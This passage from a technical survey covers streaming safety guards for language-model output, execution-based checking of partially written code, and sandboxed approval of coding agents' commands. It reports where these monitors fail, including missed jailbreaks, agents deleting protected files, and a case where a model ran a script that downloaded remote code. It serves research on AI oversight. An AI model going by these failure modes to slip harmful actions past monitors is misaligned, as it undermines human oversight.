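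An experiment with Kelp shows how badly this can work. It was scored by F1, which runs from 0 to 1 and combines the share of harmful responses the classifier catches with the share of its flags that are correct. On prompts from WildGuard, a safety dataset, a version with ordinary training scored 0.84 when only its last verdict counted. When a flag at any token was enough to reject the response, as in real use, it scored 0.51. The second rule can only add flags, so the whole drop must come from false alarms. If F1 is for the harmful class, as is usual, the two scores imply that more than 60% of the responses flagged under the second rule were harmless.

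Li and colleagues fixed most of this by changing the training objective. The new objective trains the classifier to match the response's label on the last ten tokens and to score the first ten as harmless. In between, it penalises frequent changes in the score and any fall in the estimated risk. F1 was 0.85 when only the last verdict counted and 0.83 when any token could flag the response. The objective assumes that a response never becomes harmless again once it has turned harmful. That is reasonable for text already on a user's screen, but not for a private draft that the model may still correct. The objective also trains the classifier to pass the first ten tokens of every response, even when they are harmful.

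NExT-Guard needs no new classifier. It uses a sparse autoencoder, a tool that breaks activations down into many features of which only a few are active at once. For each feature *j*, Fang and colleagues take its highest value anywhere in a response and compare harmful with harmless responses:

*s*ⱼ = (mean in harmful − mean in harmless) / (standard deviation in harmful + standard deviation in harmless).

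The method keeps the features with the highest *s*ⱼ, typically 32. During generation, a token's risk score is the sum of these features' values, each multiplied by its *s*ⱼ.

Another solution is to collect finer labels. In *SentGuard*, Yu, Wang and colleagues (2026) cut responses at the ends of sentences and labelled the resulting prefixes as safe, uncertain or unsafe. They took more prefixes from around the first harmful sentence, where the correct verdict changes. Their dataset, StreamSafe, has 62,000 full and partial conversations. A guard trained only on complete responses caught 61.3% of the harmful responses in the WildGuardTest test set within two sentences. Training it on partial responses as well raised this to 88.7%. PGuard's developers labelled segments within each response, which takes less work than labelling every token, and trained the classifier at positions near the end of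 each segment.

### How false alarms add up

A guard that checks 500 times has 500 chances to stop a harmless answer. Suppose each check raises a false alarm with probability *q*, independently of the others. The chance that at least one of *n* checks stops the answer is

1 − (1 − *q*)^*n*.

A guard that checks every token with a false alarm rate of 0.1% per token would stop 39% of harmless 500-token answers. A guard that checks every sentence with a rate of 0.5% per sentence would stop 12% of harmless 25-sentence answers, although its error rate per check is five times as high. To stop no more than 1% of these answers, the first guard would need a rate of about 0.002% per token and the second about 0.04% per sentence.

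In practice, errors are correlated because consecutive checks cover almost the same text. The check at token 301 covers the same 300 tokens as the previous check, plus one more. A guard that misclassifies a medical question as a request to hurt someone will probably do so again at the next token, while an answer about gardening may never be flagged. In *PGuard*, over 95% of the responses that one type of its classifier flagged on S-Eval, a set of risky prompts, had scores above 0.5 for at least 20 consecutive tokens. This figure includes correct flags, but it shows that neighbouring scores move together.

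The rate per check is therefore a poor guide to the rate per response. A guard that raises false alarms at 0.1% of tokens would stop only 0.1% of harmless answers if those answers triggered an alarm at every token and the rest triggered none. It would stop 50% if no answer triggered more than one alarm. Finding the rate that users experience requires running the guard over complete harmless answers and counting each answer as stopped if any check would have stopped it.

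Yu and colleagues report that SentGuard stopped 7.41% of harmless responses on average across five test sets. Guards designed for finished text did much worse on partial text. On StreamSafe, which includes the model's reasoning before its answer, the Qwen3Guard version for complete responses flagged 45.4% of harmless responses at some point, and the streaming version flagged 12.6%.

Even a rate per response depends heavily on what people ask. In the same tests, Qwen3Guard-Stream-8B stopped 15.3% of harmless responses on Safe-RLHF, a set of responses about sensitive subjects, and 3.8% on XSTest, which includes harmless requests that resemble dangerous ones. In *PGuard*, it stopped 0.8% on XSTest, 1.9% on real chatbot conversations from WildChat, and 0.12% on Alpaca, a set of simple instructions. The two sets of tests may have used different responses and settings for XSTest.

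False alarms matter more when harm is rare. If one response in 1,000 were harmful, a guard with SentGuard's average false alarm rate would stop about 74 harmless responses for each harmful one. The rate would probably be lower on ordinary traffic, since safety tests concentrate on difficult subjects, but a builder should measure it on real traffic before using the guard to stop responses.

### Comparing step sizes

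Yu and colleagues argue that a sentence is the best unit to check, since a single token carries too little meaning and a full response comes too late. In their tests, SentGuard caught on average 90.5% of harmful responses within the first two sentences, compared with 69.6% for Qwen3Guard-Stream-8B, which checks every token. SentGuard also stopped fewer harmless responses, 7.4% compared with 9.3%.

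These results favour SentGuard but don't isolate the effect of step size, because the guards had different training data and one of the five test sets came from SentGuard's own dataset. The experiment with partial responses also suggests that training explains much of the difference, since the detection rate rose by 27 percentage points even though both versions checked at every sentence.

The detection rate also counts sentences from the beginning of the response rather than from the beginning of the harm, so a guard can score well by triggering too early. Fang and colleagues had people mark the harmful words in 300 responses and compared the first marked word with the place where each guard triggered. NExT-Guard's triggers were fairly close to the human marks, while Qwen3Guard-Stream-8B tended to trigger earlier. They attribute this to the guard reacting to individual keywords. Alternatively,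 a guard that also reads the request may be correctly predicting a harmful answer. Stopping a harmful response early does no damage in either case, but a guard that reacts to keywords would also stop harmless answers containing them.

PGuard can score every token or, to save computation, only every tenth. Its memory updates at every token either way, so each score covers the full prefix. Of the harmful responses it caught when scoring every token, it flagged 86.3% within the first 10% of their length. Scoring every tenth token would delay detection by at most nine tokens.

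Reports of NExT-Guard's accuracy conflict. Fang and colleagues report an average F1 of 0.843 for responses in three datasets, compared with 0.757 for Qwen3Guard-Stream-8B. The entire lead comes from Safe-RLHF, where NExT-Guard scored 0.888 and Qwen3Guard-Stream-8B scored 0.617; on the other two datasets, the Qwen guard was slightly ahead on average. *PGuard* reports a score of 0.930 for the same Qwen guard on Safe-RLHF, counting responses that the guard labelled "controversial" as harmful. It also reports that NExT-Guard averaged only 0.634 over eight datasets and stopped 44% of harmless responses in two tests of excessive refusal. That comparison comes from a competing team, which had to choose NExT-Guard's settings itself and applied the method to an ordinary language model instead of a guard.

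### What the guard has not read yet

Wang, Shen and colleagues (2026) argue in *FreoStream* that streaming guards both refuse harmless text and miss attacks because they don't have the rest of the answer. The words "how to overdose" could begin dangerous advice or a paragraph about prevention, and a guard that stops the answer at "overdose" does so before it is clear which. In a jailbreak, a request worded to get around a model's safety training, the harm may lie in the combination of many pieces that look harmless on their own.

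Their measurements support the first half of this diagnosis better than the second. They tested two Qwen guards with 0.6 billion parameters on answers from GPT-4o. The guard that read the finished answer wrongly refused 17.1% of harmless requests, while the guard that checked every token wrongly refused 28.4%. But the finished-answer guard let more attacks succeed, 30.3% compared with 17.2%. The pattern was the same for answers from DeepSeek-R1. If missing context were the main reason for missed attacks, the guard with the full text should have missed fewer. The two guards were trained differently, so the comparison is imperfect, but repeated checking could explain both differences, because a guard that can trigger at any token has more chances to stop both harmful and harmless answers.

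FreoStream adds a second judgement. When the streaming guard flags a token, a copy of the guard with extra trained weights writes a short prediction of how the answer will continue, reasons about the text and the prediction together, and produces a second verdict. The system stops the answer only if both verdicts are "unsafe". With GPT-4o, this reduced wrong refusals from 28.4% to 7.2%.

A second judgement of this kind can only overrule alarms, so it can't catch an attack that the first guard missed. To catch such attacks, Wang and colleagues retrained the first guard, and the share that succeeded fell from 17.2% to 12.5%. They describe the retraining as a way to transfer safety knowledge from the reasoning examples, but their formulas suggest that these examples change only the size of each training step, not its direction. Let *g*ₛ be the gradient from safety examples, meaning the direction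 in which ordinary safety training would change the guard's weights, and *g*ᵣ the gradient from the reasoning examples. The method keeps only the part of *g*ᵣ that lies along *g*ₛ, which is *c*·*g*ₛ for some number *c*, and adds it to *g*ₛ to get (1 + *c*)·*g*ₛ. Most of the gain may therefore come from additional safety training on prompts rewritten as attacks. The comparison without this method doesn't show whether it does, because its result of 17.1% is almost the same as the original guard's.

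A separate, slower guard can also make the second judgement. In a trial of *PGuard* on Alpaca, the classifier inside the model flagged 0.215% of responses, and a guard that reasons before it answers reviewed only those. The system then blocked 0.056% of all responses. Reviewing only the flagged responses takes about 99.8% fewer calls to the slower guard than reviewing every response.

The main results come from different tests, so the rows below are not a ranking.

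| Guard | Checks after every | Harmful content | Harmless responses stopped | Added time or computation |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3Guard-Stream-8B | token | 69.6% caught within two sentences | 9.3% | a second model |
| SentGuard | sentence | 90.5% caught within two sentences | 7.4% | 36 ms per check, mostly hidden |
| Kelp | token | F1 of 0.83 on WildGuard | included in F1 | 0.42 ms per token |
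| NExT-Guard | token | F1 of 0.84, or 0.63 in a rival's tests | 44% in the rival's tests | a second model |
| FreoStream, with GPT-4o | token | 12.5% of attacks succeeded | 7.2% | two small models |
| PGuard, on Qwen3.5-9B | ten tokens | F1 of up to 0.86 | 4.2% to 6.4% in refusal tests | up to 1.9% lower output speed |

### Holding text back until it passes

A system cannot take back text it has already shown, so it must either delay the display or accept that users will sometimes see the beginning of something it later stops. This choice remains even if the guard needs no computing time, because a sentence may become recognisably harmful only at its last word.

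SentGuard holds the model's output in a release buffer. The buffer collects tokens until they form a sentence or a similar chunk, and the guard then checks the whole prefix up to that point. Meanwhile, the model writes the next chunk into the buffer. The user sees a chunk only after it passes the check.

Yu and colleagues calculate the delay for an average response of 160 tokens in 16 chunks, with 36 milliseconds for each check. At 40 tokens per second, a chunk of ten tokens takes 250 milliseconds to write:

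| Chunk | The model finishes it at | The user sees it at |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | 250 ms | 286 ms |
| 2 | 500 ms | 536 ms |
| 16 | 4,000 ms | 4,036 ms |

Without the buffer, the first token would appear after 25 milliseconds. With it, each token appears 36 to 261 milliseconds after the model writes it, but the complete response arrives only 36 milliseconds late. If the model had to pause for every check, the total delay would be 16 × 36 = 576 milliseconds.

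The overlap works only while checking a chunk takes less time than writing one. At 320 tokens per second, the model finishes a chunk in about 31 milliseconds, which is faster than the guard can check it, so the total delay grows to 102.5 milliseconds. These figures come from a simulation with a fixed time per check, and a busy server could be slower. Longer sentences also make the user wait longer for the first words, about 0.8 seconds for a 30-token sentence at 40 tokens per second.

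A second judgement can require a much larger buffer. FreoStream's second guard may write up to 1,024 tokens before it reaches a verdict, which would take about ten seconds at 100 tokens per second. FreoStream lets the model continue its answer in the meantime, so the system would have to hold back all the text written during those seconds to avoid showing anything it might later reject.

A builder who accepts that users may see some unwanted text can display tokens immediately and stop when the guard triggers. If the guard checks every ten tokens, up to nine more tokens can appear before the next check, which takes less than a quarter of a second at 40 tokens per second. That delay may be tolerable for an insult, but not for a password or dangerous instructions that work. The system can silently rewrite only text it hasn't yet shown, so the buffer also limits how much it can repair.

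### Judging code line by line

Wang, Sun and colleagues (2025) found in *SemGuard* that semantic errors, which a compiler doesn't report, made up more than 60% of the faults in programs by two coding models with about 7 billion parameters. Tests can reveal these errors, but usually only once the program is complete. SemGuard's trained evaluator reads the problem description and the unfinished program, and estimates after each line whether the code is still correct, without running anything.

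The training data had to show where programs go wrong, so Wang and colleagues took solutions from CodeNet, a large collection of programming competition submissions, and paired wrong solutions with correct ones by the same person. They kept pairs that shared more than 90% of their short token sequences. They treated the line that differed as the error, or, if several lines differed, had the language model DeepSeek-V3 compare the two programs and pick the line where the mistake began. They then cut both programs after that line, which left two almost identical beginnings, one correct and one incorrect. The Python dataset, SemDiff, has 123,522 such fragments from 998 problems.

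These labels don't show whether a program can still be completed correctly, either. In one example, the evaluator scored a program 0.38 after the line `C = []`, and the system rejected the line because the score was not above 0.5. But creating an empty list can't rule out a correct completion unless it overwrites a value the program still needs. The evaluator had learned that programs that begin this way tend to fail.

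After a rejection, the system discards the current line, multiplies the probability of the line's first token by 0.8 and writes the line again. It makes at most three attempts, and if none passes, it keeps the highest-scoring one and continues. A mistaken evaluator therefore can't block generation forever, but the finished program can contain lines that the evaluator rejected.

The main competitor was ROCODE, an earlier system that runs each finished program on test cases and goes back if a test fails. With DeepSeek-Coder 6.7B as the generating model and an evaluator with 1.3 billion parameters, the results on SemDiff were:

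| Method | Programs that pass | Tokens per problem | Seconds per problem |
|---|---|---|---|
| No checking | 30.3% | 110 | 6.1 |
| Several programs, filtered by tests | 33.3% | 231 | 8.4 |
| ROCODE | 35.8% | 254 | 32.5 |
| SemGuard | 38.1% | 176 | 13.0 |

The test set has 120 problems, and each method tried them three times, so SemGuard had only eight more successes than ROCODE in 360 attempts (137 against 129). SemGuard's gain over no checking is more convincing because it appeared with all six generating models, although it was sometimes below three percentage points. On LiveCodeBench, a set of newer and harder problems, SemGuard raised DeepSeek-Coder's success rate from 7.7% to 10.0%, but ROCODE did slightly better than SemGuard with one model, CodeLlama 7B. These generating models are all weak by current standards, and an evaluator of this size might find far fewer mistakes in a strong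 model's code.

Whether checking helped depended on the evaluator's quality. When Wang and colleagues replaced the evaluator with a 770-million-parameter model, 28.3% of programs passed, fewer than with no checking.

They also criticise how ROCODE chooses where to go back to. It relies on entropy, which measures how widely the model spread its probability over possible next tokens, but entropy can be high at a harmless variable name and low at a wrong condition. In one program for balancing brackets, the mistake was on line 10, but ROCODE went back to line 3 and discarded correct code.

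To measure how often this happens, they examined rollbacks in 30 problems from each of three datasets. For every rejected fragment, they generated 100 continuations and counted the rejection as false if any passed the available tests. Three programmers judged the remaining fragments. On average, more than half of ROCODE's rollbacks were false in every dataset, while for SemGuard the share was at or below 40% in most problems. These are shares of rollbacks, not of all lines checked, so they don't show how often SemGuard would interrupt a program that was correct so far.

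## Running unfinished code to see whether it works

Running code on an input shows what it does, because the run produces an exception, an output or a set of variable values. A compiler can show that a program's names and types fit together, and a trained classifier can estimate whether the program is on the right track, but neither shows how it behaves. However, a function that stops in the middle of a loop usually can't run as it stands, and if a patched version fails, the missing code may be the reason. The code also needs a sandbox, an isolated environment with restricted access to files and the network, because nobody has reviewed it yet.

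### Making a fragment executable

Suppose a model is writing a function that merges two logs in order of time and has reached the tenth line:

```python
def merge_logs(a, b):
    merged = []
    i = 0
    j = 0
    while i < len(a) and j < len(b):
        if timestamp(a[i]) <= timestamp(b[j]):
            merged.append(a[i])
            i += 1
        else:
            merged.append(b[
```

Software can make this run in six steps:

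1. Cut the text after the last complete statement, which removes line 10.
2. Close the open blocks. The empty `else` gets a `pass`, which does nothing, and the loop gets a temporary `break`.
3. Supply missing names and imports. The model hasn't written `timestamp` yet, so a stand-in returns the first five characters of a log entry.
4. Choose inputs, here two short logs.
5. Run the result under a time limit.
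6. Read the exception, the output or the values of the variables.

```python
def timestamp(line):
    return line[:5]        # stand-in for the missing helper

def merge_logs(a, b):
    merged = []
    i = 0
    j = 0
    while i < len(a) and j < len(b):
        if timestamp(a[i]) <= timestamp(b[j]):
            merged.append(a[i])
            i += 1
        else:
            pass           # fills the empty block
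        break              # ends the loop after one pass

merge_logs(["09:00 start", "09:20 stop"], ["09:10 error"])
```

The run raises no exception. At the end, `merged` contains the 09:00 entry, `i` is 1 and `j` is 0. The function returns `None`, because the model hasn't written a `return` yet.

Without the `break`, the run would never end. On the second pass, 09:20 is later than 09:10, so Python takes the `else` branch, and the line that should advance `j` is missing. Wu, Li and colleagues (2026), in *Do Uncertainty Signals Help?*, insert a `break` into open `while` loops for this reason. A second pass would also start from values that the missing lines should have changed, so an exception there might not indicate a fault in the code the model has written. The sealor for Rust stopped open loops after one pass for the same reason. An open `for` loop usually ends by itself, but its later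 passes are just as unreliable, so it makes sense to stop it after one pass too. Until the model has finished the loop, however, the check misses faults that appear only on later passes.

The first two steps are easy to automate. In *Execution Guided Line-by-Line Code Generation*, Lavon, Katz and Wolf (2025) try to parse the fragment. If that fails, they add `pass` to the last line and try again. If that also fails, they delete the last line and repeat the process on what remains. In the example, line 10 has to be deleted, but `else: pass` parses. In one of their prompts, they also ask the model to use as many short lines as possible, so that more prefixes can run.

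Missing names are harder to handle. In generative compilation, the method designed by Mündler-Sasahara and colleagues, a placeholder never runs, so it only has to satisfy the compiler. When unfinished code is run, the placeholder has to return a value that the next lines can use, and a bad placeholder causes additional failures.

Scripts that run from top to bottom need less preparation. In *Executing as You Generate*, Sun, Lin and colleagues (2026) run each complete top-level statement while the model writes the next one, in a session that keeps all variables. Their software adds nothing to the code, and in data analysis the files supplied with the task serve as the input. A whole loop or function definition counts as one statement. Because a block can look complete and still continue, the software waits for one more token to see whether a new statement begins. A fault inside a function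 stays hidden until a later statement calls the function.

### Telling a faulty prefix from an incomplete one

Suppose the model had written `or` instead of `and` on line 5, and the test merges an empty log with a log of one entry. Python enters the loop because the second log has an entry. Line 6 then looks up the first entry of the empty log and raises an `IndexError`. The input is valid, the model wrote every line that led to the error, and nothing it adds after line 10 can run before line 6. The finished function will crash in the same way unless the model later defines the whole function again, so this exception is a good reason to reject the prefix.

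Most other failures don't:

| Result of the run | Cause | Verdict |
|---|---|---|
| `IndexError` on line 6 for an empty log, with `or` on line 5 | finished code | fail |
| `NameError` for `timestamp` | the helper may come later | unknown |
| `None` instead of the merged log | no `return` yet | unknown |
| time limit reached, without the `break` | the line that advances `j` is missing | unknown |
| `TypeError` because the stand-in returned nothing | the stand-in | unknown |
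| no exception | these lines ran on this input | unknown |

A `NameError` inside a function can come from a misspelling or from a helper that the model hasn't written yet, the same ambiguity that delayed the Rust checker. At the top level of a script, a `NameError` is a real fault, because the statement runs before any code below it can define the name.

A checker that ignores these differences rejects good code. If it compared the return value with the expected log after every line, it would reject every prefix of `merge_logs` that stops before the `return`, even a correct one. The system would then discard a correct loop, or the model might add an early `return` to pass the test. *ROCODE* (Jiang, Dong and colleagues, 2024) avoids this by running unfinished code on the test inputs and comparing outputs only once the code is complete.

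It is hard to say how often the confusion occurs in practice. In a diagnostic run by Wu and colleagues with CodeLlama-7B on HumanEval, failed assertions caused 1,102 of 1,889 rollbacks, or 58%. A failed assertion means that the code ran but gave the wrong result, which is a real fault if the function is finished. The count doesn't separate finished functions from unfinished ones, however. `NameError` was also among the most frequent triggers and caused 283 rollbacks.

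When an exception is real, acting on it early seems to help with repairs, at least in scripts. Sun and colleagues stopped seven models at the first exception and gave them the partial script with the error message. They also gave the same models the complete script with the same message. On three sets of data analysis and plotting tasks, the repair success rate was higher with the partial script in all 21 comparisons, by 2.1 to 44.3 percentage points. Sun and colleagues suggest that a complete script makes the model stick to its original, flawed logic. On GitChameleon, which tests whether code fits a particular version of a library, the partial script did worse for four models, by up to 15 points, and better for only one. A repair counted as successful if the original error didn't return, so these figures don't measure how many scripts gave the right answer.

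### Using traces to guide the next token

Lavon and colleagues' method, Execution-Guided Classifier-Free Guidance (EG-CFG), runs several possible continuations of an unfinished function and gives the model a record of what happened. It does not classify the unfinished function as faulty or correct.

At the start of each line, the system generates three candidate continuations with beam search, a method that extends several likely texts in parallel. Each candidate adds two to eight lines. The system makes the candidates executable with the parsing rule described above, removes duplicates and runs the rest on every test case. It records a trace of each run: the lines executed, the variables' values and types, the function calls, the return values and any errors. It then inserts the candidates and their traces into the prompt, with a note that the candidates may be incomplete.

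For every token in the line, the model now computes two distributions. Let *P*(*w*) be the probability of token *w* without the traces in the prompt, and *Q*(*w*) its probability with them. The system scores each token by

log *R*(*w*) = log *P*(*w*) + γ [log *Q*(*w*) − log *P*(*w*)]

and picks the token with the highest score. At γ = 0, the traces have no effect. At γ = 1, the system uses only the distribution with traces, and above 1 it exaggerates the difference that the traces make.

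Suppose the only plausible tokens are `<` and `<=`. The model assigns them probabilities of 60% and 40% without traces, and 40% and 60% with traces. After rescaling, `<=` gets 50% at γ = 0.5, 60% at γ = 1 and 88% at γ = 3, so a large γ can turn a modest change in the probabilities into a much larger one.

The system keeps the same traces until the line ends, then generates new candidates. If the finished program fails, the system starts again with other settings, and it stops at the first program that passes. Lavon and colleagues varied the length of the candidates, the randomness of the sampling, the prompt and γ, which gives up to 192 combinations per problem.

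### What the traces contributed

The main tests used DeepSeek-V3-0324, a large open-weight model. MBPP-ET and HumanEval-ET contain the same problems as MBPP and HumanEval but test solutions more thoroughly. CodeContests consists of competition problems. MapCoder, the comparison method in the table, uses several model agents that write complete programs and then repair them. The figures are percentages of problems solved.

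| Benchmark | Model alone | MapCoder | EG-CFG |
|---|---|---|---|
| MBPP | 82.8 | 87.2 | 96.6 |
| MBPP-ET | 64.8 | 69.6 | 73.0 |
| HumanEval | 82.9 | 97.0 | 97.0 |
| HumanEval-ET | 79.2 | 81.7 | 87.2 |
| CodeContests | 41.8 | 50.3 | 58.2 |

The MBPP result probably overstates the benefit, because the prompt contains the test cases, the search ends when a program passes them, and the same tests appear to decide the score. With the additional tests in MBPP-ET, the gain over the model alone shrinks from 13.8 points to 8.2. For DeepSeek-Coder 1.3B, a much smaller model, it shrinks from 33.8 points to 17.2. At least half of the gain remains in both cases. The comparison would be more informative if the model alone had also received up to 192 attempts, with the tests used to choose among them.

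Lavon and colleagues also tested the small model on MBPP with parts of the method removed. The complete method solved 83.2% of the problems, and the model alone solved 49.4%. With a single continuation instead of several, the result fell to 58.2%. On MBPP-ET, that version was only one point better than the model alone, so seeing how alternatives behave seems to matter more than seeing a trace at all. Replacing the full traces with the final values of the variables gave 76.4% on MBPP. Fixing γ at 1 gave 75.2%, though part of that drop may come from having fewer settings to try.

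With all settings running in parallel, the large model took an average of 271 seconds per MBPP problem. MapCoder took 284 seconds, and LPW, a method that plans and then repairs, took 88. These are waiting times, and the total computation is much larger because many runs happen at once. The method also requires token probabilities, and Lavon and colleagues chose their hosting service partly because it provided them.

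### Writing results into the program as comments

*Execution-Guided Within-Prompt Search for Programming-by-Example* (Verbruggen, Tiwari and colleagues, 2025) uses execution without changing how the model picks tokens. The task is to find a program given a few inputs and their expected outputs. In one example, the program must turn `Program-Synthesis` into `PS` and `Large--Language--Model` into `LLM`.

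The system samples four possible next lines and discards any that don't run. It puts the others into one function, runs them on the examples and adds the results as comments:

```python
def f(a):
    v1 = a.split('-')
    # first input: ['Program', 'Synthesis']
    # second input: ['Large', '', 'Language', '', 'Model']
    v2 = a[0]
    # first input: 'P', second input: 'L'
```

The comments show the empty strings that the double hyphens produce. GPT-4o then wrote a line that takes the first letter of each word in `v1` and skips empty words, which solves the problem. Without the comments, it had written code that didn't account for the empty strings.

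The process repeats up to eight times and stops when any variable matches all the expected outputs. The software then deletes the lines that the solution doesn't use. A poor line does little harm, because the model can ignore it and continue from a better one without a rollback, although the poor line still takes up space in the prompt.

The method depends on the execution results. When Verbruggen and colleagues left out the comments, the search did no better than sampling complete programs independently with a similar budget. With the comments, it did better on four of five benchmarks. The exception was a set of puzzles about lists of integers, where intermediate values gave little hint of the rule. In a broader comparison, the method came first on three benchmarks and second on two. A separate prompt that rated each line worked better when the system sampled more lines at once, but it used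 about twice as many tokens.

The experiments covered only code without loops or branches. Each line of such code is a complete step that has a value as soon as the model writes it, so there are no half-finished blocks to handle. Extending the method to ordinary functions would require the repairs that `merge_logs` needed. Small-scale trials with older and smaller models also went significantly worse, because those models didn't keep to one line at a time or couldn't use the comments.

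### Building the missing context automatically

The stand-in for `timestamp` was easy to write, but a fragment from a large project may need objects with dozens of attributes, installed libraries and files on disk. *AgentExecutor* (Chen, Li and colleagues, 2026) uses language models to build this context and place it before the fragment. The models work as agents, meaning they run commands and use the results to choose what to try next.

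One agent installs libraries and creates files. A second writes the setup code, runs it with the fragment and receives a report of the lines that didn't run. After ten attempts in a row without improvement, the system removes those attempts from the second agent's prompt, so that the agent continues from its best result. If some lines still haven't run, a third agent writes a program that tries combinations of values. For instance, if two earlier setups used *a* = 1, *b* = 2 and *a* = 3, *b* = 4, the program also tries *a* = 1, *b* = 4 and *a* = 3, *b* = 2. About 14% of the fragments needed this step.

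Chen and colleagues tested the system on 462 answers from Stack Overflow, a site for programming questions, and 1,000 functions from open-source Python projects. They counted a line only if it ran without crashing.

| | Stack Overflow | Open-source functions |
|---|---|---|
| Lines run without any setup | 43% | 4% |
| Lines run with Treefix, the best earlier method | 79% | 79% |
| Lines run with AgentExecutor | 94% | 90% |
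| Fragments in which every line ran, over several setups | 91% | 80% |
| Time per fragment | 156 seconds | 222 seconds |
| Cost per fragment | $0.023 | $0.055 |

The fragments averaged only nine lines, so building a new setup after every line of a longer program would be far too slow. A builder could create the setup once when the model begins a function and reuse it as the function grows. The fragments also had endings but lacked the surrounding context, so a function that stops in the middle of a loop would still need its blocks closed.

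A more serious problem with using this system to find faults is that its agents look for values that let the code run, so they tend to avoid inputs that would make it crash. With the faulty `or` in `merge_logs`, two ordinary logs would get every line to run at least once, and the agents would have no reason to try an empty one. In one of Chen and colleagues' examples, a fragment opened an image at a Windows path that didn't exist on the test machine. The second agent replaced the whole image library with an imitation, and every line ran, but the imitation may accept calls that the real library would reject. Chen and colleagues acknowledge that running more lines doesn't make a run closer to the code's real use.

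### The need for trustworthy inputs

An exception is evidence of a fault only if the finished code has to handle the input that caused it. `merge_logs` crashes if it receives `None` instead of a list, but that is a fault only if callers may pass `None`. The choice of inputs also determines what a run can reveal, since two ordinary logs would never expose the `or` on the first pass.

Expected outputs can be wrong as well. Lavon and colleagues examined the 17 MBPP problems that their method failed with the large model. They found invalid tests in nine and judged the rejected program correct in all nine. The example prompt in their paper also contains a wrong test. The task is to find the first character that doesn't repeat, and the expected output for `aabc` is `c`, although `b` comes first. If a method puts tests and traces into the prompt, such an error can lead the model away from a correct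 solution.

Benchmarks come with tests, but everyday requests often don't, a limitation that Lavon and colleagues acknowledge. A builder can look for inputs in the user's examples, the project's existing tests and the data files that a script will read. A model can also write the tests, but if it has misunderstood the request, it may repeat the misunderstanding in them. Inputs without expected outputs are still useful while the code is unfinished, because an exception can show that the code so far is wrong, whereas a wrong return value can't.

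If reliable tests with expected outputs are available, some should be reserved for the final evaluation. Wu and colleagues use only public tests during generation and run the hidden ones afterward, so a program can't pass the final evaluation merely because the system kept trying until those tests succeeded.

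## Using a sandboxed run as a test of safety

Running code in a sandbox can show whether it does damage as well as whether it works. For judging safety, the return value matters less than the code's effects: which files it changed, which servers it tried to reach, which programs it started and which data it disclosed. If the system allows a step only when its effects are acceptable, the run serves as a safety oracle, a procedure the system relies on to decide whether a step is harmful.

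### Comparing effects with a policy

Suppose a user wants to free disk space by deleting two folders of old build files, `/work/build` and `/work/build-old`. The builder's policy for this task could be:

```text
Changes and deletions:  only /work/build, /work/build-old and their contents
Reads:                  Python's own files, and /work except /work/.env
Connections:            none
New processes:          none
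Printed output:         no passwords or keys
```

The policy excludes `.env` because files with that name often contain passwords. The model is writing a Python script and has just finished its first loop:

```python
import shutil
from pathlib import Path

for folder in Path("/work").glob("build*"):
    shutil.rmtree(folder)
```

The loop deletes every folder in `/work` whose name starts with "build". Whether that is harmless depends on which folders exist, and the code doesn't show this. The system therefore copies the current state, runs the loop on the copy and compares the effects with the policy:

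| Observed effect | Verdict |
|---|---|
| deletes `/work/build` | allowed |
| deletes `/work/build-old` | allowed |
| deletes `/work/build_scripts` | violation |
| no connections, new processes or output | allowed |

Because of the third deletion, the system discards the copy, reports the problem to the model and has it rewrite the loop. If the new loop names the two folders, all its effects fit the policy, and the system keeps the changed copy as the current state.

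Missing code causes less confusion in a test of safety than in a test of correctness. No later line will bring back the deleted folder, so the system can reject the loop without waiting for the rest of the script.

### Letting a model judge the effects

A fixed policy is predictable, but someone has to write it for each task, because deleting a folder can be the purpose of one task and harmful in another. In *Shall We Approve?*, Wu, Chen and colleagues (2026) instead use a language model to judge the shell commands that a coding agent proposes. Their system, Caper, takes a snapshot of the agent's container, a sandbox without network access. It then runs the command in the container and records the command's requests to the operating system, but doesn't show the agent the output yet. A separate model, the approver, reads the user's task, the conversation, the command and a short report of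 its effects, which lists attempted network connections even though they fail. The approver then decides whether the effects fall within the task. If it approves, Caper keeps the changed container, so the command doesn't have to run again. Otherwise, Caper restores the snapshot and gives the agent a reason.

One of their tests has 102 tasks in which the user asks for a tool that looks harmless but also deletes or overwrites a protected file. Each task has a safe version with the same request and command but a harmless tool. The table shows how the results depended on what the approver received.

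| Information for the approver | Dangerous tasks that ended in harm | Safe twins blocked |
|---|---|---|
| no approver | 71.6% | none |
| conversation and command | 17.6% | 61.8% |
| the same, with predicted effects | 3.9% | 61.8% |
| the same, with observed effects | 7.8% | 1.0% |

Giving the approver predicted effects prevented slightly more harm than giving it observed ones, a difference of four tasks. Running the command helped because the approver stopped blocking harmless work. A weaker approver also blocked far fewer safe twins when it received observed effects. But it let more harm through (33.3%, compared with 25.5% without them), so an accurate record helps only if the approver interprets it correctly.

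Caper was also tested on 682 tasks from *SABER* (2026), a benchmark that records changes to the workspace because safe and harmful commands can look equally plausible. The agent caused harm in 19.7% of tasks when no approval was required and in 6.7% with Caper, a lower rate than with any of the six existing systems tested. But it also completed fewer tasks safely, 48.6% compared with 57.4%, because it declined or paused more often.

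The system has to reach its verdict before the effects become permanent. *APEX-Harm* (2026) describes a case in which Claude Opus 5 ran a suspicious helper program and requested an inspection of its code in the same message. Claude gave its warning after the program had already downloaded and run a remote script. The sandbox also has to keep the program from changing anything outside it. In a test from *V³AST-Bench* (2026), an agent tried out a suspicious program on copied files in a folder it called a "sandbox". The agent then rejected the program, but the program had already written ten junk files to the real workspace. Some effects, such as sending an email, can't happen on a copy. *AOSpec* (2026) describes a system that runs an agent's likely next actions in advance and excludes effects it can't isolate.

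### Effects that look harmless without more information

Even a complete record of effects may lack the facts that make an action harmful. *Policy-Invisible Violations in LLM-Based Agents* (Wu and Gong, 2026) gives an example in which a user asks an assistant to share an onboarding folder with a colleague. One file in the folder contains pay information that only HR and managers may read, but neither the file's name nor the assistant's tools reveal this. The log entry "shared three files with David Liu" would therefore look normal even if Liu were not allowed to read that file.

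Wu and Gong's system, Sentinel, keeps a graph of people, documents and access rules. It translates each proposed action into changes to the graph, applies them to a copy and checks seven rules on the result. If a rule fails, it blocks the action or asks for clarification. Because Sentinel simulates the action instead of executing it, the verdict also depends on whether the translation is right. In a test with 60 risky and 60 safe cases, each of five models carried out 54 to 59 of the risky actions without Sentinel. Sentinel's decisions were correct 93.0% of the time, compared with 68.8% for a filter that checked only content. Wu and Gong describe these conditions as favourable, since the graph already contained the relevant facts. In a real organisation, someone would have to collect those facts and keep them up to date.

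### What a clean run leaves open

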